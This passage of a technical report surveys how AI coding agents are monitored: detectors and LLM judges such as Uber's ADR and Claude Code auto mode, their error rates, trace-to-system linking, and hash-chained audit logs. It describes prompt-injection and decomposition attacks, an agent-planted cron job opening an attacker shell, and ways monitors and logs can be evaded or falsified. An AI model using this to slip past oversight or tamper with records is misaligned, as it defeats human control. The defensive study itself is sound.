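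*Tether* (2026) describes a program that enforces such rules on the system calls of coding agents. If Tether classifies an agent as having read secret files, it blocks the agent's further actions. This classification can be wrong because Tether observes only system calls. Tether also raised false alarms when agents contacted outside hosts that the task had not declared. It prohibits background processes and database interactions to stop agents from bypassing it. That policy would not suit the clean-up agent or the support agent, which both need a database.

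Other detectors estimate what a sequence of actions means instead of matching it to a rule. King and colleagues list several, including ChainWatch, which applies a hidden Markov model to MCP tool calls. A hidden Markov model infers a hidden state from a series of observed events. Here the events are the tool calls, and the hidden state is which of six stages of an attack the agent has reached. If an agent listed files, read a credential and then uploaded something, the estimate might move towards the later stages.

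Neither approach would help with the support agent's misdirected report, because the sequence of steps was the same as in the correct run.

### Departures from past behaviour

A detector can also learn what an agent normally does and flag changes. Arigbabu (2026), in *Entropy-Based Observability for AI Agent Behavior*, proposes measuring these changes with entropy, a number that describes how spread out a set of choices is. For tool use, the formula is

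H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

where pᵢ is the share of calls that went to tool i. If an agent makes all its calls to one search tool, the entropy is 0 bits. If 10 of every 100 calls go to a second tool, it rises to 0.47 bits, and if the agent divides its calls evenly among four tools, it is 2 bits. An operator might set an alert for a sudden rise in a type of task that has historically needed only one search tool. A fall can be informative too, because an agent stuck in a loop keeps calling the same tool.

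Arigbabu applies the same formula to other parts of a trace:

| Measure | What it counts | What a high value might mean |
|---|---|---|
| Action entropy | Types of step | Useful exploration, or indecision |
| Trajectory entropy | Whole sequences, such as search, read, answer | The agent solves the same task in many ways |
| Outcome entropy | Results of repeated runs | Unstable results |

According to Arigbabu, moderate trajectory entropy with low outcome entropy is often a good sign, because the agent varies its method but still gets consistent results. Information gain measures how much the agent's uncertainty falls after it gathers evidence, but many agents don't report the probabilities needed to calculate it.

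Tool entropy does not reflect the arguments passed to each tool. The support agent calls three tools once each, so its tool entropy is log₂ 3, or about 1.58 bits, whichever address it writes to. The measures also depend on how someone defines a step. In one of Arigbabu's tests, two agents built with different frameworks had identical entropies because both produced the same five-step planning trace.

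Arigbabu tested the measures on 72 synthetic runs and six runs of real agents but reported no detection rate. The paper presents the measures as descriptions of behaviour that can help reviewers choose which traces to inspect. It is still unknown how often an entropy alert would point to a harmful action.

### A second model that judges the actions

A second language model can read the user's request and judge whether the agent's actions fit it. In the *StepShield* test, GPT-4.1-mini did this one step at a time and flagged 95.4% of the harmful runs and 5.6% of the clean ones. Felicia and colleagues also tried a cheaper arrangement, in which the 847 rules decided the high-confidence cases and the model handled the rest. This combination flagged only 75.9% of the harmful runs and 44.4% of the clean ones. Adding rules can therefore make detection less accurate if they decide too many cases before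 the model reads them.

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a classifier, itself a language model, that can block an agent's action before it happens. Fixed rules allow read-only tools and edits inside the project folder. The classifier checks most other tool calls, including shell commands and web requests. It first gives a quick yes or no and leans towards blocking. If it flags a call, it reviews the same evidence again and writes out its reasoning.

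The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's other text or the tools' results. Anthropic removes the agent's text because arguments in it could lead the classifier to label a dangerous action safe, and the results because they may contain injected instructions. But without them, the classifier can't determine where the agent got a detail. If the agent cancels job `abc123` and the user never mentioned that job, the agent may have found the identifier in a query or made it up.

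In one of Anthropic's examples, which closely resembles the bulk deletion, a user asked an agent to "clean up old branches" and the agent started deleting branches from the shared copy of the code. Auto mode should block this because the request was vague and the deletion irreversible. It would probably block the wildcard deletion for the same reasons. The misdirected report is harder because catching it would depend on which domains the operator had listed as trusted.

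#### What the judge should look at

The wording of the judge's task can matter more than how much text the judge reads. *Towards a Unified Misuse Monitoring Benchmark* (Pramod, Oldfield and Bibi, 2026) compared 17 monitor configurations on about 6,200 synthetic traces. Some traces contained prompt injections, and others contained decomposition attacks, in which the user splits a harmful goal into innocent-looking requests.

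Two of the monitors read the whole conversation so far. One judged the overall intent of the requests and had an AUROC of 0.960 on decomposition attacks but only 0.521 on injections, barely better than guessing. The other judged the agent's current action and scored 0.952 on decomposition attacks and 0.985 on injections. An injected instruction leaves the user's request looking innocent, so a monitor has to focus on the agent's actions.

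A judge can also misapply a clear instruction. *Tether* tested Claude Code's auto mode on the same runs as its own program and found that most of auto mode's false alarms came from blocking file edits that the task explicitly allowed.

### Uber's ADR

The most detailed account of an agent monitor in production comes from Uber, where Li and colleagues ran their system, ADR, for more than ten months. It grew to cover over 7,200 computers and more than 10,000 agent sessions a day.

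ADR's sensor runs once an hour on employees' MacBooks and takes 0.18 seconds on average. It reads the history files of Cursor, Cline and Claude Code, then rebuilds each session from the prompts, the agent's reasoning, and the MCP tool calls with their arguments and results. It also collects MCP server settings and lists of installed packages. Li and colleagues considered using a gateway, but it would have captured less context and required changes to the agents' software. A sensor like this works only if its developers know where an agent keeps its files, so it could easily miss a home-made agent.

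The detector has two stages. GPT-4o screens every session for warning signs, such as requests involving credentials, permission changes and phrases typical of prompt injection, and clears only those that seem clearly harmless. Claude Sonnet 4 examines the rest, and can look up a tool's source code, company policies and a library of known attack techniques before reaching a verdict. Before deployment, a separate set of agents invents attacks and tries them in a sandbox, and the most useful discoveries are added to the library.

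#### Results on two benchmarks

Li and colleagues built a benchmark, ADR-Bench, from Uber's experience, public incidents and earlier benchmarks. It has 42 malicious tasks and 260 benign ones, averaging 28.5 tool calls per task. They also used AgentDojo, a public benchmark in which agents do jobs such as banking and booking travel while tool results contain hidden instructions.

ADR was compared with three other detectors. LlamaFirewall, from Meta, combines a safety classifier with simple rules. GuardAgent uses GPT-4o to check behaviour against 47 security policies. ALRPHFS compares behaviour with 301 known attack patterns and sends unclear cases to a stronger model.

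| Detector | ADR-Bench: attacks caught, of 42 | ADR-Bench: false alarms, of 260 | AgentDojo: attacks caught, of 38 | AgentDojo: false alarms, of 55 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ADR | 28 | 0 | 38 | 3 |
| ALRPHFS | 17 | 34 | 32 | 3 |
| GuardAgent | 9 | 30 | 27 | 8 |
| LlamaFirewall | 8 | 40 | 37 | 21 |

ADR caught 67% of the attacks in ADR-Bench with no false alarms. On AgentDojo, it caught every attack but also flagged three of the 55 benign tasks (5.5%). Li and colleagues describe this as three false alarms in 93 tasks, although only the benign tasks could have produced a false alarm.

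On ADR-Bench, ADR caught all nine attacks that bypassed security controls or disrupted operations, but only one of the five that abused permissions. Five attacks are too few to give a reliable detection rate, but the misses matter because permission abuse is the type of attack closest to an agent doing harm with access it legitimately holds.

Li and colleagues then removed parts of ADR to find out what each contributed. Without the source-code lookup, recall fell from 66.7% to 57.1%, probably because a tool's description may not reveal what its code does. Removing the policy lookup made almost no difference. Removing the screening stage raised recall to 80.5%, so the screening must have dismissed some real attacks as harmless. Removing it also produced two false alarms and increased the cost by 29%.

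The full system cost an average of $0.024 per task. If production sessions cost the same, reviewing 10,000 sessions a day would cost about $240, probably much less than paying the analysts who read the alerts.

The comparison favours ADR somewhat, because the same team built both ADR and the benchmark, and adapted the other detectors to the benchmark. LlamaFirewall's recall was 19% on ADR-Bench and 97% on AgentDojo, so a detector's measured recall can depend heavily on the benchmark. Uber has released the benchmark and ADR's code, so others could repeat the test.

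#### The credential filter

Li and colleagues also report a precision of 97.2%, but for a different program, a filter that scans prompts for passwords and keys before Cursor or Claude Code sends them. It looks for known formats and random-looking strings, without using a language model. Of the 212 distinct strings it flagged, 206 were real credentials.

The result shows that fixed patterns work well when the target has a recognisable format, but it isn't evidence about how well ADR judges actions. Recall is also unknown, because nobody counted the credentials that the filter missed.

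### How many alerts would be real?

A detector that raises no false alarms in 260 benign tasks could still have a false-positive rate as high as about 1.15%, at 95% confidence. If the true rate were p, the chance of seeing no false alarms in 260 independent tasks would be (1 − p)²⁶⁰, which falls to 5% when p is about 1.15%. At 10,000 sessions a day, that rate would produce about 115 false alarms.

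Suppose that five of those sessions are harmful. This number is invented, since Li and colleagues don't report the real one. At ADR's benchmark recall of two-thirds, it would catch 3.3 of them on an average day, so its precision would be

3.3 ÷ (3.3 + 115) ≈ 3%

An analyst would have to open about 35 alerts to find one harmful session. The precision changes dramatically with the false-positive rate:

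| False-positive rate | False alarms a day | Precision |
|---|---|---|
| 0% | 0 | 100% |
| 0.1% | 10 | 25% |
| 1.15%, the upper bound from ADR-Bench | 115 | 3% |
| 5.5%, ADR's rate on AgentDojo | 550 | 0.6% |

For half the alerts to be correct, the false-positive rate would have to be about 0.033%. Demonstrating a rate that low would take around 9,000 benign sessions with no false alarms. Uber has that many sessions in a day, but someone would have to establish that they were benign.

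Other published figures need the same adjustment. Felicia and colleagues calculate that if 8.1% of runs were harmful, a share they consider realistic, 60% of GPT-4.1-mini's alerts would be correct, compared with 8.9% of alerts from the 847 rules. If five runs in 10,000 were harmful, fewer than 1% of the model's alerts would be correct. Pramod and colleagues report recall at a false-positive rate of up to 10%, which would mean as many as 1,000 false alarms a day at Uber's volume.

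#### What happened in production

All these calculations use benchmark tasks in place of production sessions, but a benchmark's benign tasks may be shorter, tidier or less varied than employees' real work.

Li and colleagues report that Uber's analysts labelled 34% of the sessions ADR sent them in production as real threats and 49% as false positives. The other 17% were real but not malicious, mostly the work of Uber's own security testers. Many of the false positives were sessions with a lot of context, such as the analysis of a large codebase.

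This is far better than 3% but well below the perfect precision on ADR-Bench. Li and colleagues argue that many of the false positives were cautious referrals of complicated sessions, which the benchmark wouldn't count as errors, but an analyst still has to read them. The paper doesn't give the number of alerts or estimate how many harmful sessions ADR missed, so ADR's false-positive rate and recall in production are unknown.

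Vendors' alert rates are even harder to interpret. Codenotary, which sells a monitoring platform for agents, claims that about 7% of more than three million daily agent interactions triggered a detection, according to Techzine. These detections include excessive token use and abnormal retries as well as exposed passwords, and Techzine does not say how many were confirmed. The figure is unverified, and a poorly tuned detector could reach the same rate with false alarms.

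### Detecting an agent's own mistakes

Most benchmarks contain attacks because researchers can plant them and know the right answer. Anthropic also tested auto mode on real mistakes from its staff's sessions. It calls these "overeager" actions, in which the agent understands the goal but does more than the user authorised, for example by using a credential it happened to find.

| Test set | Measure | Quick check only | Both checks |
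|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls | Harmless calls blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real overeager actions | Dangerous actions missed | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data | Dangerous actions missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second check removed most of the false alarms but let more of the dangerous actions through. It missed real mistakes about three times as often as synthetic leaks, so a detector's score on planted attacks may overstate how well it catches real mistakes.

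In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised that the action was dangerous but wrongly concluded that the user had authorised it. For example, a request to "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) does not authorise the agent to overwrite the change's history. The agent in the database example also took a loose phrase as permission, so a classifier can evidently make the same mistake as the agent it is checking.

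With only 52 cases, the true miss rate could plausibly be from about 9% to 30%. The cases also came from sessions in which an employee refused the action or someone flagged it later, so the sample excludes mistakes that nobody noticed.

#### Later tests of auto mode

A judge may still be better than a person clicking "approve", which is often the alternative. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes an experiment in which 1,053 paid testers each received one clearly dangerous command among their normal permission prompts. The testers refused 13.6% of these commands, while auto mode blocked 89%. Testers refused about 17% early in a session, but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. They weren't working on their own projects, which may have made them less careful.

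Anthropic also compared manually approved and auto mode sessions among real sessions that its safety system had flagged for review. Serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested occurred in 6.3% of the manually approved sessions and 2.4% of the auto mode sessions. A model graded the harm. Users had chosen their own mode, so some of the difference may come from differences in the users and their tasks.

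Two outside companies also tested auto mode, although Anthropic arranged both tests and published the results. Apollo Research, which evaluates AI safety, inserted synthetic attacks into real coding sessions. After Anthropic strengthened the classifier, its miss rate on these attacks fell from 12% to 7%. Anthropic had never had access to some of the attacks, so the improvement was probably not limited to familiar examples.

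Trajectory Labs tried 72 prompt-injection scenarios ten times each, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude models in auto mode. This is limited evidence that auto mode helps, because only 0.09% of the attacks succeeded against Anthropic's latest models even with no permission checks. The results for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol are better evidence that a reviewer helps. The attacks succeeded 19.03% of the time with full access and 5.83% of the time with Codex's automatic reviewer, a reduction of about two-thirds.

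### Alerting afterwards or blocking first

Because ADR collects data hourly, the support agent's report could be in a stranger's inbox for up to an hour before the detector had any record of it. A late alert would still be useful for damage that staff can reverse, for example by restoring deleted rows from a backup, but they couldn't take back the email.

According to Li and colleagues, passwords and keys had often already left Uber by the time ADR detected them, and there were too many alerts to review by hand. Uber therefore added the credential filter, which can block a prompt before the agent sends it.

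A detector that blocks actions has to be fast. ADR's deeper review took an average of 29.7 seconds on ADR-Bench, which would be tolerable once per session but not before every shell command. A blocker also has less evidence than a detector that runs afterwards, because it must work without the action's results or anything that followed.

False alarms cause less trouble, however, when a detector blocks calls than when it sends alerts to an analyst. When auto mode blocks a call, it gives the agent the reason, and the agent usually finds another way to continue. If each harmless call had an independent 0.4% chance of being blocked, a session with 100 checked calls, all harmless, would have a 33% chance of at least one false block. A developer might hardly notice, but if the same false alarms went to an analyst, about a third of such sessions would need investigation, which is too many to handle.

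A blocked agent may find another way to do the same harm, as Codex tried to do when Sophos' software blocked its downloads. Auto mode instructs the agent not to work around a block, and asks the user to take over after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session.

#### Flagging the right step

A blocker also has to react at the right moment. Felicia and colleagues measured how often a detector's first alert in the harmful runs it flagged came at the first harmful step or within the next three. GPT-4.1-mini managed this in 89% of those runs, but the 847 rules did so in only 23%, about the same as alerts at random steps (24%). On average, the rules fired five steps too early, on code that was still harmless, so many of their apparent catches were false alarms.

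Pramod and colleagues found that timing was a problem for models used as judges too. In one of their traces, an agent drafts a phishing email and, 11 messages later, commits to sending it. The agent then collects the stolen passwords and mails them to the attacker. A monitor gets credit only if its first flag falls between that commitment and the final mailing. On decomposition attacks, the monitors that judged actions did so in only 33% to 50% of harmful traces, mostly because they flagged earlier preparatory steps.

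This score is stricter than an operator needs, since stopping a harmful run too early still prevents the harm. Early flags are more of a problem when the agent would have behaved properly anyway. Pramod and colleagues also tested traces in which the agent refused at what would have been its first harmful action. With most of the models they tried, the monitors still flagged 28% to 48% of these traces.

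For high-stakes changes to production systems, Anthropic still recommends that users review Claude's actions themselves. Its experiment suggests that this works only if reviewers get few enough prompts to read each one carefully.

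## How can agent traces be joined to system records, and how far can each be trusted?

An investigator can join an agent's trace to system records through a shared identifier, the account behind a request, process ancestry, closeness in time, or text that appears both in the model's output and in a command or file name. A shared identifier links the records directly, but with the other methods the investigator has to infer the link and can pick the wrong event. Even a correct link can join false or incomplete records, because each record is only as reliable as the program that wrote it.

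### Matching identifiers, accounts, processes and text

Trace context provides a shared identifier when every program records it, but an operating system's own records of processes and files don't include it. Sometimes another value can link the records instead. For one email in Zhao's constructed example, the agent's log includes a permission, and the authorisation server's log shows that a person approved that permission for the same recipient and attachment. Four seconds after the approval, the mail gateway logged a delivery to that recipient, with an attachment that had the same hash. Zhao leaves another email undecided because the agent's log had no permission or correlation identifier and the authorisation server had lost its log for that hour.

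Giving each agent its own account makes it possible to link audit log entries to that agent, which can't be done when the agent acts under a user's account. But the account doesn't identify the task. If the support agent handles 40 tickets at once, all its database queries come from the same account.

Running each task in its own container solves this for events on the host. King and colleagues gave every session a new container and a sensor that followed only the processes in it. They tested the method on 30 sessions, running three at a time, and none of the 8,240 recorded events had another session's tag. The method doesn't cover agents built into code editors, agents that run directly on a shared machine, or agents that were already running when the sensor started.

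Process ancestry links a command to the harness that started it, even if several shells and scripts come in between. But if one harness process serves many conversations, ancestry alone can't identify which conversation the command came from.

Matching text can link a system record to the model response that caused it. If a response contains the path `/etc/passwd` and a process then opens that file, the link is probably right. A common name such as `README.md` is weaker evidence, because many tasks read a file with that name. Many actions have no matching text. When a model's response runs `npm test`, the tests may open thousands of files whose names never appear in the model's output.

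### How matching on time goes wrong

In this invented example, two subagents work in parallel on the same machine, and a monitoring tool links each system event to any model response in the preceding 500 milliseconds:

| Time (seconds) | Event |
|---|---|
| 0.00 | Response A tells the first subagent to run `run_tests.sh` |
| 0.05 | The harness starts `run_tests.sh` |
| 4.00 | Response B tells the second subagent to read `README.md` |
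| 4.10 | A process opens `README.md` |
| 4.30 | A process deletes the folder `/srv/uploads` |

The test script deleted the folder as its last step, so response A caused the deletion. The tool instead links the deletion to response B, which came 0.3 seconds before it. An investigator who trusted this link would blame the wrong subagent and might search the README for an injected instruction.

A five-second window would include response A but also keep response B, so the tool would have two candidates. Matching text wouldn't link the deletion to either response, because neither mentions `/srv/uploads`. The process tree would point to response A, because the process that deleted the folder descends from `run_tests.sh`, and only response A contains that name.

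Clocks on different machines may also disagree, which makes the machines' records harder to match. A one-second difference is enough to put every true match outside a 500-millisecond window.

### AgentSight

AgentSight, which Zheng and colleagues built, joins agent traces to system records using process ancestry, time and matching text. It uses eBPF, a Linux feature that runs small programs inside the kernel after checking that they are safe.

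One eBPF program attaches to the functions that OpenSSL and similar libraries use to encrypt and decrypt web traffic. It copies the agent's prompts just before encryption and the model's responses just after decryption, so the operator doesn't have to change the agent's code or set up a gateway. Another program records when the agent or any of its descendant processes starts a process, opens a file or connects to another machine. It discards events from all other processes.

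Outside the kernel, AgentSight maintains the process tree and links each action to a recent model response within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds. It also searches the system calls for file names, web addresses and commands from the response. It then sends the joined trace to a second language model with instructions to act as a security analyst. That model returns a written explanation and a confidence score.

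In the staged attack with the malicious README, AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37. The second model's output gave the trace a high attack score, with the explanation that the agent's actions didn't fit its stated goal. In another case, six coding agents worked on one project, and AgentSight produced 3,153 events after merging. The trace showed some agents repeatedly waiting for files that others had locked.

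These case studies show that the method can work, but not how often it fails. Zheng and colleagues didn't report how many harmless sessions the second model would flag, or how many of AgentSight's links were wrong. They call the links definitive, which is too strong for a method that relies partly on timing.

#### The cost of running it

Zheng and colleagues timed Claude Code on three tasks, with and without AgentSight, and ran each test three times. Bao, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *AgentLoupe*, later timed AgentSight on similar tasks, with five runs each, alongside a successor they had built:

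| Task | AgentSight, first test | AgentSight, later test | AgentLoupe |
|---|---|---|---|
| Understanding a code repository | 3.4% slower | 4.5% slower | 4.5% slower |
| Writing code | 4.9% slower | 2.5% slower | 8.0% slower |
| Compiling a program | 0.4% slower | 1.7% slower | 7.7% slower |

AgentSight's average overhead is 2.9% in both tests. The figures for single tasks are less certain because model response times vary from run to run. In the later test, compilation appeared to run 0.1% faster with one version of AgentLoupe than with no monitor, so small differences are probably noise.

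#### What it cannot observe

AgentSight records activity only on the machine it runs on. If the support agent calls an MCP server on another machine, AgentSight can record the connection but not the server's database query.

AgentSight, running on the agent's machine, could record the wrong address in the support agent's email even if the harness had content capture turned off, because the address is in the model's response. Its store of prompts and responses therefore needs the same privacy protection as a full-text trace. AgentSight couldn't read the reasoning that Codex receives, because that reasoning is still an encrypted block after the traffic is decrypted.

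### Links that survive a delay

An agent can write a file that another program uses hours later. In Bao and colleagues' main example, an attacker asks an agent to install an hourly job. An hour later, cron, the program that runs scheduled jobs on Linux, starts the agent's script, which opens a connection that gives the attacker a shell. AgentSight's filter would discard the script's events because the script's parent process is cron. The hour-long delay is also far longer than AgentSight's time window.

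AgentLoupe deals with this by labeling files with the number of a prompt. It reads model traffic as AgentSight does, but gives each independent prompt a number inside the kernel, which child processes inherit. When a numbered process writes a file, AgentLoupe stores the number with the file, and any process that later opens or runs the file receives it. Network connections can also pass the number on.

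In the cron test, AgentLoupe linked the request, the script, the scheduled run and the network connection. In a second test, one session wrote a malicious instruction into `AGENTS.md`, a file of standing instructions for coding agents, and a later session followed it. AgentLoupe linked the two sessions through the file. Bao and colleagues argue that AgentSight would miss both links because of its design, but they leave a direct comparison on such attacks to future work.

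Labels can also spread too far. If an agent edits a settings file that 20 programs read, all 20 could receive the agent's number, even if the edit affected only one. AgentLoupe limits this by assigning a new number to each independent prompt and recording its connection to the old one. Bao and colleagues haven't measured how many links are false or missing.

#### Tracking files without reading prompts

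*Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) tracks the same kind of path without reading model traffic. In the paper's test, an agent's script wrote and renamed a file, and an unrelated program on the same machine then read it. Langfuse, a product that records traces from inside an application, lost the path at the file because trace context doesn't travel through an ordinary file. Agent-Warden reconstructed the path in all 120 runs and increased running time by 0.2% to 3.5%. Every run used the same planned scenario, so the result shows that the tool is consistent but is weak evidence of how it would handle varied work.

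Agent-Warden doesn't record some kinds of file access, such as mapping a file into memory. It also keeps its labels in memory, so a reboot erases them, and the kernel may drop them earlier if memory runs short. An attacker's scheduled job that first ran after a reboot would no longer be linked to the agent. AgentLoupe also keeps its labels in kernel memory, so they probably have the same weakness.

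#### Recording links directly

A runtime, the software that runs an agent, can avoid some guesswork by recording links between events as they happen. *Agent libOS* (2026) describes a runtime that stores the links between a model call, the tool it led to and any human decision, and lists any missing evidence. These links cover only what passes through the runtime, so they can supplement a host sensor but not replace it.

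A system can also use labels to block actions. *ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) turns an instruction such as "run tests before committing" into a rule that the kernel enforces. The rule applies even when a script makes the commit, which a check on tool calls could miss. ActPlane slowed agents' work by 1.9% and a compilation of the Linux kernel by up to 8.4%.

### What joined records add to detection

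King and colleagues also gave their ten detectors application records and system calls together. When the test attacks resembled those in the training data, all ten detectors performed best with the combination. With unfamiliar families of attack, seven performed best with the combination and three with system calls alone.

Combining application records with system calls helped most where neither was enough alone. For attacks that manipulated the agent's preferences, the average AUROC was 0.687 with application records, 0.701 with system calls and 0.834 with both. King and colleagues joined the records only by session, without linking each system call to a model response. An operator may therefore get much of the benefit from a simple and reliable join, such as matching records by container when each session runs in its own.

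A correct link still doesn't show that an action was harmful. *Self-State Attacks on Self-Hosted AI Agents* (2026) tested attacks that make an agent change its own stored files. System records identified the agent as the writer in all 21 successful attacks and in all 21 matching harmless runs. For the wildcard deletion, a perfect join would trace the lost rows to the model's response, but someone would still have to compare that response with the instruction.

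### Who writes each record

A trace from the harness is only as reliable as the harness. A bug can omit a tool call from the trace, and an intruder who controls the process can deliberately omit calls or add harmless ones that never happened. ADR's sensor has the same weakness even though it is a separate program, because it reads history files that the agents' own software writes.

A host sensor gets its evidence from the kernel, so the harness doesn't directly control what the sensor records. But an intruder who controls the kernel can hide events from the sensor. Cui and colleagues assume that the kernel and the program that loads their sensor are trustworthy, and *ActPlane* makes a similar assumption. King and colleagues ran their sensor inside the agent's container, where a malicious agent could try to interfere with it through Linux's debugging interface. The attempt would appear in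 the log, but their detectors didn't look for it.

A provider's log is outside the operator's control, so an intruder on the operator's machine can't edit it. But the operator has to trust the provider to record requests accurately, keep the records and hand them over. The same applies to logs kept by the company that runs a remote MCP server.

#### Traccia's hashes

Traccia is a monitoring platform that presents OpenTelemetry traces as audit evidence. *TRACCIA* (Naik, Saroj and colleagues, 2026) describes how a library inside the agent's program creates spans, passes trace context to other services, removes recognised personal data before export, and adds SHA-256 hashes of the inputs and outputs. Traccia then combines the traces with human reviews and incident reports in one file, adds a hash of the file, and labels the evidence with the relevant articles of the EU AI Act.

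The hashes can show only that the text hasn't changed since the library hashed it, although Naik and colleagues claim that the hashes guarantee a faithful record of the original interaction. If the agent's program gave the library a false output, the hash would match it. The hash on the exported file is also weak protection if it is unsigned and stored only with the file, because anyone who edits the file can calculate a new hash.

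The paper illustrates the platform by following a loan-approval assistant through it. It includes no test in which someone tries to falsify or delete a record.

### Protecting records from later changes

The simplest protection is to send records promptly to a machine or account that the agent can't control. An intruder who later takes over the agent's machine can stop or falsify new records but can't change those already sent. The records may still have been false when they were sent, and the administrator of the new location can still change or delete them.

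Append-only storage allows new entries but blocks edits and deletions. This protects existing records from ordinary users and from anyone who steals a password with limited rights. An administrator may still be able to turn the restriction off or replace the whole store. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026) points out that outsiders still have to trust an operator who runs its own append-only log.

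#### A hash chain with three entries

A hash chain makes later changes detectable by including each entry's hash in the next entry. *aiAuthZ* (2026), a system that checks agents' permissions on a separate machine, calculates the hash of entry n as

hₙ = SHA-256(hₙ₋₁, n, contents of entry n)

where hₙ₋₁ is the previous entry's hash. For the database clean-up, the chain might look like this, with invented and shortened hashes:

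| Entry | Contents | Previous hash | Own hash |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Instruction: "clean up old records" | `0000` | `a41c` |
| 2 | Tool call: delete every record | `a41c` | `7be0` |
| 3 | Result: success | `7be0` | `d93f` |

Suppose someone wants to hide the mistake and changes entry 2 to "delete records from before 2015". The hash of the new contents is `52c8`, which doesn't match the stored `7be0`. If the person replaces `7be0` with `52c8`, entry 3 still lists `7be0` as the previous hash, so the chain breaks there. The person would have to update that value too and recalculate entry 3's own hash, which might become `19ae`.

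After that, the chain is consistent again. An investigator could discover the change only by comparing the new final hash, `19ae`, with a copy of the original, `d93f`, stored somewhere the person couldn't reach. *aiAuthZ* lets operators copy the latest hash to outside storage for this reason. Operators can also calculate the hashes with a secret key, so that someone who can edit the log but doesn't have the key can't rebuild the chain.

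Deleting entry 3 is even easier, because the first two entries form a valid chain by themselves. *BioFirewall* (2026), which describes a screening system for AI used in genome design, recommends storing both the number of entries and the latest hash separately from the log. A verifier can then tell whether the log has been shortened.

No version of the chain shows that an entry was true when the program wrote it. If the harness had wrongly recorded "delete records from before 2015" from the start, every hash would still be correct and the outside copy would still match.

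A hash-chained log can still let an operator delete private data. *aiAuthZ* chains hashes of the sensitive text and the decisions, and stores the encrypted text alongside the chain. The operator can erase old text and still verify that the agent made a request and what the system decided.

### Finding records that are missing

A hash chain also can't reveal an action that nobody recorded, so finding missing records takes further checks. *Agent Flight Recorder* (2026), which describes a hash-chained log for agents, explicitly excludes completeness from its goals.

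One check is to number the records. *HANSARD* (2026) proposes independent recorders for five channels: model calls, tool calls, messages between agents, changes to memory, and delegation. Each channel has its own running count, so an investigator who finds tool calls 41 and 43 but not 42 knows that a record is missing. A program other than the agent's harness has to assign the numbers, because the harness could hide a call by not numbering it. The counts can't reveal an action taken through a channel that has no recorder.

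Gaps in a regular signal can reveal when recording stopped. Ganesan's proposed authenticator would sign such a signal, along with a record of every action it approves or refuses. It would also send the latest hash in its chain to each service the agent uses, so that the service has a copy to compare later. Actions that need no credential, such as editing a local file, would not pass through the authenticator, so the harness would have to report them, and the log would label them as reported by the harness.

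#### Comparing two independent records

A stronger check is to compare the harness's record with one it didn't write. *Hearsay* (2026) describes a separate program that logs every request the harness sends to the model and every reply. The program chains the entries with hashes and has a public service timestamp the latest hash. Software then compares the two records. Anything that appears only in the outside log is an omission from the harness's record, and anything that appears only in the harness's record is an invention or a rewrite. Some differences are legitimate, such as an error message the harness writes itself, so each record format needs a short list of exceptions.

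*Hearsay* uses software for this comparison because giving readers the outside log didn't improve their answers. The readers mostly cited the agent's own words, and the log can prove that the model produced those words but not that they are true.

If the harness in the clean-up example hid the call to `delete_records`, this comparison would reveal it, because the outside log would contain the model's request. Confirming that the deletion ran would still require the database's log.

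The second record must also cover every relevant action. In Zhao's example, the mail gateway recorded the unmatched fourth email because every external email has to pass through it. If the agent could also send messages through a web form, the two logs could match even though both omitted a message.

Ordinary faults can also lose records, so a gap does not prove tampering. *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* (2026) reports tests in which a log silently lost 9.66% of its records when two programs wrote to it at once, and 31.32% when eight did. Those rates apply only to that log, but operators can run the same test on their own by sending a known number of records from several agents at once and counting how many arrive.
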